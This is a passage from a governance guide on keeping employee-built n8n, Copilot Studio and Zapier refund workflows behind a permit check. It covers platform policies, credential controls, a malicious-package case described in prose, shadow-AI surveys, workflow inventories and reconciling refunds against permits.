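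The shop can't exclude HTTP Request everywhere, because the refund workflow needs it to reach the decision service. Node type policies can make exceptions for single projects. The policy for the whole installation can allow, deny or delegate each type of step. No project can override a denial. If the policy delegates a step, n8n blocks it in each project until that project's administrator allows it. The shop could delegate HTTP Request and allow it only in IT's project, where `refund_order` calls the decision service. This restricts Dana only if she isn't the administrator of her own project, since she could otherwise allow the step there too.

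n8n checks these policies when someone saves, publishes or runs a workflow, and when an agent uses a tool. It also checks workflows that arrive through an import or from a code repository. A block sends an event to the company's logging system if the company has connected one.

The exclusion list blocks whole steps, so it can't block a connector's refunds without also blocking its payment lookups. In the forum thread *Block access to specific node action*, mfranma asked how to stop n8n users from creating incidents in ServiceNow, a service for IT requests, while leaving the rest of the connector available. Another member replied that n8n had no built-in way to do this. The suggested alternatives were to block the whole step, use a credential with fewer rights, or maintain a modified copy of the connector. For payments, a credential with fewer rights is the best option if the provider offers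 one, because a key without refund rights can't issue refunds from an HTTP step either.

Code steps in n8n can't import additional software modules unless an administrator permits them, according to n8n's *Nodes*. Since version 2.0, n8n explains, code steps also can't read the server's environment variables by default, so they can't read a payment key stored there. An administrator can switch off either protection, perhaps to make one workflow run, and should check both before relying on them. Langdock, another maker of AI workflow tools, gives administrators a simpler option, a switch that controls the Code step for every workflow in a workspace.

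Companies can use n8n's `workflow.preExecute` hook to refuse workflows with unapproved payment steps. However, n8n's *v3.0 Breaking changes* says that a run refused by this hook no longer leaves an execution record. Companies that use the hook this way need to add an alert to the hook itself, or repeated attempts to run such a workflow could go unnoticed.

### Data policies for Copilot Studio

Administrators can use data policies to restrict connectors in Copilot Studio, which is part of Microsoft's low-code Power Platform. A data policy sorts connectors into Business, Non-business and Blocked groups. Nobody can use a Blocked connector where the policy applies. Business and Non-business connectors both work, and their names serve only to separate two groups that, according to Microsoft, can't share data with each other.

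Suppose the shop rebuilds the refund workflow in Copilot Studio, with the order system in Business and the payment provider in Non-business. Dana couldn't build a workflow that reads an order and then pays a refund, but she could still use Non-business connectors alone to build one in which someone types an amount into a form and the provider pays it. The two groups keep sensitive data away from the wrong services, but they don't control spending. To prevent unchecked refunds, the administrator has to block the payment connector and give builders a custom connector to the gateway.

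The administrator also has to classify the HTTP connectors, which a policy can handle like any other. A new policy blocks nothing at first, because Microsoft places every connector in Non-business until the administrator moves it. Connectors that Microsoft adds later go into a default group, which the administrator can change to Blocked. Even then, according to Microsoft's *Configure data loss prevention policies for Power Platform*, new connectors that can't be blocked go into Non-business.

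Those exceptions include Outlook, Teams, SharePoint and OneDrive for Business, some of which are among the most important connectors for outgoing messages. An older policy may still block one of these if the block was set when Microsoft allowed it. The next time someone edits that policy, the administrator has to move the connector out of the blocked group before saving. An unrelated edit could therefore restore email access for every builder the policy covers.

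Two finer controls go below the level of the connector:

- **Action control** allows or blocks single operations. Microsoft gives the example of letting makers read data through a connector but not modify it. The shop could allow payment lookups and block refunds. Connectors gain new actions when their publishers update them, so the administrator should also choose to block new actions. Action control doesn't work on connectors that can't be blocked, so it can't take the "send" action out of Outlook. Microsoft's *Connector action control* adds that administrators can control triggers as well, but only with PowerShell, Microsoft's command-line tool.
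- **Endpoint filtering** limits the addresses that a connector may contact. Microsoft's *New Data Loss Prevention policies for enhanced Power Platform governance* describes a policy that lets the SQL Server connector reach one test server and nothing else. Filtering covers only six connectors. Before using it to limit web requests to the gateway, an administrator should try both an address typed into a step and one that the workflow puts together during a run.

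These controls apply to agents too. Microsoft's endpoint rules cover chatbots as well as apps and flows. Rencore's *Power Platform DLP Connector*, a reference for a product that inventories these policies, includes Copilot Studio's connectors. Copilot Studio's check before each tool call doesn't cover classic agents, but a data policy should help with them because it restricts the connector.

### An allowlist that leaves out custom connectors

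Since June 2026, administrators have had a stricter alternative called advanced connector policies. Microsoft describes it as an allowlist that blocks every connector and action, including connectors added later, unless the administrator allows it. It replaces the three groups and can apply to one environment or a group of environments. If it covers Outlook and Teams as fully as this description implies, it closes the largest gap in the older policies. Blocking a "send" action and then trying to run it would show whether it does.

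According to a notice republished by Itelio, the allowlist is off until an administrator activates it, and it applies only to certified connectors, including those for MCP servers. Custom connectors stay under the older data policies. The shop's connector to its own gateway would probably be custom, as would any connector Dana built to reach the payment provider directly. A shop that switches to the allowlist therefore still needs a data policy, which can classify custom connectors by their web addresses.

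### App limits in Zapier and Make

If refunds go through the gateway, a Zapier workflow reaches it with a general webhook step and no longer needs the payment provider's app. The administrator can then block that app completely with Zapier's app controls. But the webhook step has to stay available, and a builder with a valid payment key could use it to call the provider directly. Blocking the app helps prevent accidents, such as a new colleague choosing the obvious payment step from the menu.

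A shop that uses Make should delete the stored payment connection as well as the old payment step, because a builder could attach a leftover connection to a new workflow.

### Storing a personal login

The change in n8n 2.46 that stops Dana from using the manager's login also lets any member of a team project use a personal credential in the team's workflows without sharing it first. If Dana has her own login at the payment provider, she can attach it to a payment step that has no check. Her colleagues can see that the workflow uses her login, but they can't run the workflow.

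The node and credential policies from November 2026 can restrict a type of credential, such as the payment provider's, across the installation. n8n blocks publishing of any workflow that uses that type, and runs of existing workflows fail. Before the restriction takes effect, n8n shows how many workflows depend on it. General credential types are harder to restrict. NeuralTrust's ready-made HTTP workflows, for instance, use a "Header Auth" credential, which can hold a key for almost any service. The shop's gateway key would probably use the same type, so n8n couldn't block a payment key stored that way without also blocking the gateway key.

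Some companies store their keys in a separate vault, and n8n fetches them when needed as "external secrets". From version 3.0, every project editor and administrator can use external secrets in their projects by default. A company that had limited this to certain roles has to create custom roles before it upgrades, or all its editors will gain access. If the payment key is in the vault, the upgrade could unintentionally let Dana use it.

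### Installing a component from a stranger

Anyone can publish an n8n component on npm, a public registry of JavaScript packages, and npm doesn't review the code first. In January 2026, attackers used malicious components to steal logins. *n8mare on auth street* (Raj and Plate, 2026) analyses one that posed as a connector for Google Ads. Users entered their logins in what looked like a normal form. n8n encrypted and stored the logins correctly, but when a workflow ran, it decrypted them for the component, which sent them to the attackers.

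The Hacker News (2026) listed eight malicious packages and later reported that Endor Labs, the security company where Raj and Plate work, had confirmed a ninth. A few other packages from the same publishers turned out to be harmless. The registry had removed the first eight by then.

The number of victims is unknown. The eight packages had about 28,000 downloads by The Hacker News's figures, but automated systems also download packages, and one user can download the same package many times. The most downloaded package had 8,385 downloads, but Raj and Plate give a weekly figure of just 80. The attackers had published 77 versions of it, which may have attracted automated downloads.

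The case matters for permit checks because a component runs with the same access as n8n. Raj and Plate point out that n8n doesn't isolate it, so it can read files and environment variables, contact outside servers and receive decrypted keys. An If step can't stop code that has the payment key and its own network connection.

Several n8n settings would have prevented the installation:

- Setting `N8N_COMMUNITY_PACKAGES_ENABLED` to `false` turns off all community components.
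- Setting `N8N_UNVERIFIED_PACKAGES_ENABLED` to `false` leaves only those that n8n has verified. This would have been enough unless n8n had verified one of the malicious packages, which seems very unlikely.
- A licensed customer can have n8n install components from a private registry that contains only packages the company has reviewed.
- A company can give n8n a fixed list of components, with a version and a checksum for each. n8n then removes everything else at startup, and users can't install components from the settings page.

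n8n 3.0 changes the second of these to `false` by default, and unverified components that are already installed stop loading. n8n's list of settings still gives the old default of `true`, so an administrator should set the value explicitly.

The new default can also disable a security product. NeuralTrust's check is a community component, and its documentation describes it as not yet verified for n8n Cloud. If the component doesn't load on a server, the workflow fails instead of continuing without the check. This is safer, but it still stops refunds. A shop that needs an unverified component can allow such packages and use the fixed list to block all the others.

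Step policies are a weaker defence here, because code in a package can run as soon as n8n loads it, before anyone adds the component to a workflow. In July 2026, OSV's *MAL-2026-10774* (2026), an entry in a public database of software vulnerabilities, recorded another malicious package disguised as an n8n component.

A gateway would have limited the damage, because the payment provider's key would not have been in n8n for a component to steal. It wouldn't have protected the Google Ads logins unless they had been moved to the gateway too. Raj and Plate also recommend using accounts with as few rights as possible, which limits what an attacker can do with a stolen login.

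### Building somewhere the rules don't apply

A strict policy may cover only one of the places where employees build workflows. Each n8n user has a personal space outside the team projects and can, by default, publish and share workflows from it. According to n8n's *Manage security policies*, administrators can turn off both publishing and sharing on the Enterprise plan and, for self-hosted servers, also on the Business plan. n8n explains that turning off publishing blocks only new publications, so workflows that are already live keep running. The settings page shows how many there are, but the administrator has to find them and take them offline separately.

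In Power Platform, the equivalent gap is a new or forgotten environment. Administrators can set a company-wide data policy to include or exclude particular environments. A policy that covers only listed environments will miss any created later, so it is safer to cover all environments and list the exceptions. The check before each tool call has the same weakness, because administrators connect it to individual environments or environment groups.

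No setting in n8n or Copilot Studio controls a private Zapier account. If Dana has a payment key, she can paste it into any tool and build the same workflow at home. The company can prevent this only by limiting who can create keys at the payment provider and who can connect outside apps to the shop's account.

### Making the gateway the only way out

A company that hosts its own n8n server can add a firewall that lets the server contact only the gateway, the mail service, the order system and the model provider. An HTTP step pointed at the payment provider would then fail even with a valid key. In the January case, this firewall would have stopped the component from sending stolen logins to the attackers' server.

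The firewall should be outside n8n, where neither a builder nor a component can change it. It has to allow every service the company's other workflows need, and each new service will require a request to IT. If the company leaves the payment provider's address open so that another workflow can look up payments, an ordinary firewall can't distinguish those lookups from refunds.

n8n has a network protection of its own, but it mainly serves the opposite purpose. It stops workflows from reaching internal addresses, such as the server itself and private networks, that an outsider should not be able to contact through n8n. The payment provider is on the public internet, so the default list doesn't block it. The list may well block the shop's gateway if that is on a private network. The administrator should then add the gateway's hostname to `N8N_SSRF_ALLOWED_HOSTNAMES` and keep the word `default`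 in the list of blocked ranges, because removing it would drop all the built-in protections.

A shop that uses n8n Cloud, Zapier or Make has no firewall between the tool and the payment provider. Some payment providers may let a customer restrict a key to certain network addresses. If the shop's provider does, the shop can have it accept the refund key only from the gateway's address, which gives much the same protection as a firewall.

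### The fewest settings for the refund workflow

If the shop has a gateway that checks each refund, Dana can keep full editing rights under three conditions:

1. The payment provider accepts refund requests from software only with the gateway's key, and the administrator has cancelled all the older keys.
2. Neither Dana nor any other builder can create a key at the provider or connect another app to the shop's account. They may still issue refunds by hand on the provider's website if the shop limits its guarantee to software.
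3. Dana can't change the gateway, its rules or the order data it uses, and she can't approve her own refunds.

None of these is a setting in n8n. Dana can delete steps, add an HTTP request or open a private Zapier account, but still has no key the provider would accept. The limits on steps and components still help protect the shop's other logins and customer data, and the firewall helps if someone overlooked an old key.

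The third condition takes the most care because Dana works in support, and the support team records how many items arrived broken. If a rule uses that number, she could enter four broken glasses instead of one and get a valid permit for $80. To prevent this, the shop can have a colleague record the damage whenever the refund comes from a workflow or a claim that Dana has an interest in. Support staff also shouldn't be able to edit the order system's record of the original card, the price or the total already refunded.

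If the payment key stays in n8n, the second and third conditions still apply, and the decision service takes the gateway's place in the third. The shop also needs these settings:

- The `refund_order` sub-workflow and the payment credential are in a project where Dana has no role.
- Dana isn't an administrator of the n8n installation and can't manage roles or members.
- n8n loads only components on a fixed list.
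- The Execute Command step stays blocked, and code steps can't read environment variables.

The administrator can test either arrangement by creating a test order and asking Dana to try to refund one dollar on it without a permit, using all the access she normally has. If the refund succeeds, the provider's records should help the administrator identify which key or login allowed it.

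## Why employees build outside the check, and how unchecked workflows are found

Dana's test can reveal a login that the administrator overlooked only if Dana has access to it, and it won't reveal a refund workflow that a colleague built last year and never mentioned. The shop has to search its workflow tools, credentials and the payment provider's records to find that workflow. Usage data and surveys give a rough idea of how many unchecked workflows it might find.

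### How many companies have agents that employees built

In November 2025, more than 80% of Fortune 500 companies had active agents built with Microsoft's Copilot Studio or Agent Builder, according to *80% of Fortune 500 use active AI Agents* (Microsoft, 2026). The figure comes from Microsoft's usage data, so it doesn't depend on anyone's memory or honesty. But Microsoft counts an agent as active if it is in production and had one user or one run within 28 days. A company with a single agent that answers questions about holidays counts the same as a company with thousands that make payments. The figure also includes agents that IT approved.

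Help Net Security's *AI agents inherit employee access, and nobody's watching how they use it* (2026) reports data that Nudge Security, which sells tools for finding AI services, collected from its customers' systems. Among customers with at least one agent, the median was seven agents, and about 44% had more than ten. More than half had agents on at least two platforms, and Zapier Agents was one of the common platforms. Nudge Security (2026) explained in an earlier edition that most of its percentages are shares of organizations, so they don't show how many employees build agents. Companies that buy a discovery tool may also differ from other companies.

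### What managers and employees say

Microsoft's *Cyber Pulse* reports that 29% of employees have used unsanctioned AI agents for work. The figure comes from an online survey of data security leaders that Hypothesis Group conducted for Microsoft in summer 2025. A regional Microsoft page later described it as what employees "report", although the survey didn't question ordinary employees. Microsoft's *Unifying Data Protection and AI Innovation* (2026), the main report on the 1,725 responses, doesn't appear to include the question. The figure may not be a measurement, since the leaders may have guessed instead of counting agents.

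Half of the senior British data leaders surveyed for the software company Dataiku thought that more than half of their employees used generative AI without permission, according to TechRadar's *Businesses are losing control of AI*.

Employees' answers are better evidence of what they do. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) cites a global study from 2025. *Risks of 'Shadow AI'* (Rowe) covers a November 2025 survey by Sapio Research for BlackFog, a security company. *Turns out the C-suite loves shadow AI* (Help Net Security, 2026) covers a survey by TrustedTech but gives no sample size.

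| Survey | Who answered | What they said |
|---|---|---|
| Global study | 48,000 people | 44% of employees had used AI in ways that broke company policy |
| BlackFog | 2,000 people in the UK and US | 51% had connected AI tools to other work systems without IT approval |
| TrustedTech | Employees in the UK and US | 65% of decision-makers and 31% of other employees used unapproved AI |

Someone can break an AI policy by pasting text into a chatbot, so the 44% includes many people who never built a workflow. BlackFog's question is more relevant because it is about connecting AI tools to other systems, as a connector does, but it would also count a connection that only reads a calendar. None of these surveys measured how many workflows skip a permit check, so the shop has to measure its own coverage.

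### Why people go around a control

"Shadow IT" is technology that employees adopt without the IT department's approval. In the studies that Canale and Soulis summarize, a common cause is that a department needs a tool sooner than IT can supply it. These employees are rarely malicious. If Dana asks for access to the gateway and hears nothing for three weeks, she could solve her problem that same afternoon with a private Zapier account.

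TrustedTech's respondents said they kept using unapproved tools because the approved ones didn't meet their needs or because their employer offered nothing suitable. In BlackFog's survey, 63% considered it acceptable to use AI without IT oversight if the company provided no approved option. An administrator who blocks the payment connector should therefore have the gateway connector ready the same day.

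Other employees don't know whether they are breaking a rule. About 14% of employees in TrustedTech's survey used AI tools at work without knowing whether their employer had approved them. In a no-code tool, a builder might also delete a permit check because it looks like a leftover from someone else's template.

An unexplained refusal could have a similar effect. If the check returns only "deny", Dana can't tell whether the refund is too large or the decision service is broken, and she may think connecting the payment directly would fix the problem. This is plausible, but the surveys don't measure how often it happens. The remedy is simple in any case, because the AuthZEN reply can include a reason for the workflow to show her.

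Managers can make a rule look optional. In BlackFog's survey, 21% believed their employer would ignore unapproved AI use as long as the work was finished on time. *"Game Changer" or "Overenthusiastic Drunk Acquaintance"?* (2025) reports interviews with blind and low-vision software professionals. One participant, who sometimes supervised colleagues, had "turned a blind eye" to their AI use. Participants were reluctant to give up the productivity they gained from AI, especially given their disability, so a ban may be harder on some employees than others.

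### The careless, the hurried and the malicious

Suppose the shop finds a workflow that pays refunds without a permit. The builder may have copied an old template without noticing that it lacked a check. She may have known about the check but had a queue of angry customers and no reply from IT. Or she may be sending the refunds to herself. Whatever the reason, the shop urgently needs to stop the payments and save the logs.

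A careless builder needs to learn the rule, and a template that already calls `refund_order` would help them avoid repeating the mistake. Canale and Soulis built a detector for unapproved agents that requires the user to acknowledge a notice but blocks nothing. They tested how well it detects agents, but not whether the notice changes what people do.

An employee who builds outside the check because she is in a hurry already knows the rule, so reminding her of it will do little. IT should help her move the workflow to the gateway and find out why her request took so long.

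A malicious builder will acknowledge the notice and carry on. To stop her, the shop has to control the payment key, the order records and the approval of refunds. Someone outside her team should investigate.

Secrecy alone is poor evidence of malice, since 61% of employees in the global study had avoided revealing when they used AI. Who received the money is better evidence, because refunds to the builder's own card need explaining more urgently than refunds to thirty unrelated customers.

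### OWASP's list of citizen-development risks

OWASP, a software security nonprofit, covers several of these problems in its *Top 10 Risk for Citizen Development*. The most relevant entries describe workflows that act under their builder's identity, credentials that stay active too long, applications that no longer have an owner, and missing logs.

The list is useful for an administrator deciding what to inspect, but it isn't a measurement of which risks are most common. Its introduction describes no dataset or method of ranking, and most of its examples are invented scenarios. It also includes three real-world examples:

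- In 2021, a setting in Microsoft's Power Apps that was off by default left about 38 million records open to the public.
- Veracode tested more than 100 language models on coding tasks in 2025 and found a known vulnerability in 45% of cases.
- Also in 2025, the no-code platform Passion.io left a database with over 3.6 million records unprotected.

Only the Power Apps case directly concerns a setting that citizen developers could have changed. Veracode tested models, not employees, and the Passion.io database was the platform's responsibility. None of the three involved a workflow that skipped a permit check.

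Much of the supporting material comes from people connected with Zenity, which sells security products for these tools. Zenity's *The 7 Deadly Sins of Low-Code/No-Code Security and How to Avoid them* says it was a basis for OWASP's *Low-Code/No-Code Top 10*, the forerunner of the current list. Every reference in the current list's entries on authorization misuse and asset management is an article by Zenity's Michael Bargury, who also reviewed the document. The risks are real, as n8n's shared credentials showed, but the shop shouldn't base its priorities on the order of the ten entries.

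### An inventory of workflows and credentials

OWASP recommends an inventory that covers applications, their components and their users. To build one for refunds, the shop's administrator should export every workflow from the company's tools, including those in personal spaces, and then list every key, login and connected app that can issue refunds at the payment provider. If a key doesn't match any exported workflow, someone may be using it in a tool that the administrator hasn't searched.

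The result might look like this:

| Workflow | Owner | Credential | External actions | Last run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `refund-mailbox` | Dana | Gateway key | Refund, email | Today |
| `loyalty-refunds` | Left in March | Old provider key | Refund | Yesterday |
| `delivery-dates` | Sam | Order system, read-only | None | Today |
| `test-copy-3` | Unknown | Dana's personal login | Refund | Eight months ago |

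The administrator should stop `loyalty-refunds` first, because it is still paying customers with a key that bypasses the gateway. Anyone with access could also run `test-copy-3` again, because its login still works. The shop doesn't have to delete everything it finds. Canale and Soulis cite a study of 27 shadow systems in which companies closed some systems, replaced others, and kept others with IT or the business department managing them.

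The inventory also has to be repeated. In a simple model by Canale and Soulis, the number of unapproved tools levels off at the number created each month divided by the share removed each month. If employees create 20 workflows a month and 5% of the existing ones are removed, the total levels off at 20 ÷ 0.05, or 400. Doubling the removal rate to 10% halves the total to 200. However, the model counts abandoned tools as removed, so it leaves out a workflow like `test-copy-3`, which is abandoned but still has a working login.

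Canale and Soulis argue that AI agents could make the total number of tools grow without limit, because some agents create more tools. Let *δ* be the share of tools removed each month, *φ* the share that can create others, and *σ* the number each of those creates per month. The total grows exponentially when *σφ* > *δ*. However, they know of no measurement of *σ*, and an ordinary refund workflow doesn't build other workflows.

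### Scanning for a path without a check

The inventory shows which workflows can pay refunds. The next step is to find out which of them can do so without a permit. An exported workflow lists its steps and the connections between them, so a short program can search for an unchecked path:

```
for each workflow:
    delete every connection that leaves a refund check
        through its "allow" output
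    for each step that can issue a refund:
        if a trigger can still reach that step:
            report the workflow
```

If every path to the payment goes through the "allow" output, deleting the connection from that output cuts the payment off from the trigger, and the workflow passes. If someone adds a branch for regular customers that skips the check, the trigger still leads to the payment, and the program reports it. The program also reports a payment that the builder connected to the "deny" output by mistake.

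For an agent, the program should report any payment tool other than `refund_order`, and scan that sub-workflow separately.

A step that issues refunds can be hard to recognize. A payment connector is obvious, but an HTTP step may build the provider's address during the run, and a code step could contact almost anything. The program should list these HTTP and code steps for a person to inspect.

A workflow that passes the scan still needs test refunds, because the program can't verify that the If step tests the right field or that the payment uses the checked amount. It would also pass a workflow that checks one refund and then pays it seven times.

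### Comparing refunds with permits

The payment provider's log records the refunds that actually happened, whichever tool requested them. Comparing it with the permits can therefore reveal a workflow that is missing from the inventory:

1. The administrator exports all of the month's refunds from the provider and all the permits from the decision service.
2. A program matches each refund to a permit. The permit's ID is the best link, if the gateway adds it to the refund request and the provider records it. Otherwise, the program compares the order, amount, currency, card and time.
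3. The program uses each permit only once.
4. Someone investigates every refund that is left over.

Suppose the provider lists 1,240 refunds and the program finds matching permits for 1,198 of them. That leaves 42 unexplained, and coverage is 1,198 ÷ 1,240, or 96.6%. The administrator investigates the 42:

| Refunds | Explanation | Response |
|---|---|---|
| 15 | Staff issued them by hand on the provider's website | Exclude them if the guarantee covers only software |
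| 12 | `loyalty-refunds` paid them with the old key | Cancel the key and move the workflow to the gateway |
| 9 | The service issued their permits just before midnight on the last day of the previous month | Count them as matched |
| 4 | The permit was for a smaller amount | Find the step that changed the amount |
| 2 | Nobody recognizes the key | Cancel the key and investigate |

Counting the nine refunds with earlier permits raises coverage to 1,207 of 1,240, or 97.3%. If the guarantee covers only software, the 15 manual refunds don't count, and coverage is 1,207 of 1,225, or 98.5%. The remaining 18 refunds are real failures. Fourteen had no permit, and four didn't match the permit they had.

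Permits can cover a high percentage of refunds but a smaller share of the money. If the 1,198 refunds matched at first average $60 and the other 42 average $400, permits cover only 81% of the money. Fraud may also be concentrated among the refunds that skip the check, as the earlier discussion of coverage showed.

A refund is harder to trace when the workflow uses an employee's login. Nudge Security points out that the log then shows the employee and not the agent, so the shop can't easily tell whether Dana or her workflow paid the customer. *40% of organizations struggle to retrace AI agents' actions* (Pogorelec, 2026) covers a Palo Alto Networks report on this problem. Giving each workflow its own key makes the source of a refund much clearer.

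The shop should also examine permits without a refund, because those customers may still be waiting.

### Services that nobody knows about

The comparison covers only services whose logs the shop has. Emails need a separate comparison with the mail service's log. If an employee sends customers store credit through a voucher service the administrator doesn't know about, the payment provider's log won't show it. Similarly, if a workflow copies the customer list to an unknown AI tool, the shop has no log from that tool to check.

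To find such tools, the administrator can review the permissions that employees grant when they click "allow" to let an outside service read their email or files. Help Net Security explains that data then travels between cloud services without crossing the company's network, so checks on that network don't detect it. The administrator may have many tools to examine, since the median organization in Cyberhaven's *2026 AI Adoption & Risk Report* (2026) used 54 generative AI applications.

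Expense claims can reveal paid subscriptions, but 58% of BlackFog's respondents who used unapproved tools relied on free versions. Traffic to a familiar service may not reveal an unchecked workflow either, because a connection to Zapier could belong to the company's workspace or to Dana's private account. In Netskope's *AI Security Report* (2026), 88% of respondents couldn't distinguish personal AI accounts from company ones, though Netskope sells products that address this problem.

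Software on employees' computers finds a different set of agents. Canale and Soulis's detector looks for programs that both contact an AI service and run commands on a Windows computer. In a small test on one workstation, it detected all 12 artificial agents in most runs and didn't flag otherwise identical programs that contacted a non-AI service. An agent that ran intermittently appeared in only about one scan in three. If scans were independent, it would have about a 4% chance of escaping eight hourly scans in a row. But the detector can't detect Zapier workflows, because they run on Zapier's servers.

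### Strict blocking or monitoring?

A company can block employee-built workflows until IT approves them, or allow them by default and monitor what they do. *Cyber Pulse* recommends a mix of the two, in which companies offer secure alternatives and block unauthorized apps.

The strongest reason to block is that monitoring detects a refund only after the money has left. A monthly comparison could take weeks to find `loyalty-refunds`. A nightly one would find it sooner, but the first bad payment would still go out. Bans may also work better than their critics suggest. In TrustedTech's survey, nearly a third of employees said they would keep using AI tools despite a ban and possible disciplinary action. Help Net Security presents this as a weakness of bans, but more than two-thirds didn't say they would continue.

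The main danger of blocking is that builders move to private accounts, where the company can't inspect their work. Bargury (2022), in *You Can’t Opt Out of Citizen Development*, describes a security chief whose marketing teams got around a control on cloud services and started using no-code automation. This is one anecdote from someone whose company sells a remedy. Canale and Soulis also cite a mathematical model of employees who bring their own AI tools to work. In that model, prohibition left about as much risk as baseline measures, but the result depends on the values the researchers put in.

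Help Net Security suggests that monitoring also drives some people away from approved tools. The TrustedTech survey doesn't establish this, but it found that decision-makers, the heaviest users of unapproved AI, were more likely to believe their employer monitored AI use.

Whether blocking or monitoring leaves fewer hidden workflows depends heavily on how many builders would move to private accounts. Suppose 100 employees each want to build an unapproved workflow. If the company allows the workflows and its monitoring finds 80, 20 stay hidden. If it blocks them, some builders give up and the others move to private accounts, where the company finds only 10% of their workflows. Blocking then leaves fewer hidden workflows only if 22 or fewer builders move. If 33 move, about 30 workflows stay hidden. This calculation is biased towards monitoring because it ignores the damage that the 80 detected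 workflows could do before the company finds them.

Neither side cites a trial that compares similar companies under the two approaches. The surveys also cover AI tools in general, and people might behave differently when a workflow handles money.

The shop avoids much of this problem for refunds by controlling the payment key. It can be more permissive with workflows that only read delivery dates. Workflows that handle customer data need more care, because an employee can often copy the data into a private account without a special key.

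After tightening a rule, the shop can also use its own records to see whether employees are working around it. If refunds without permits fall but employees start granting more unfamiliar tools access to their email and files, some builders have probably moved to tools outside the permit check.
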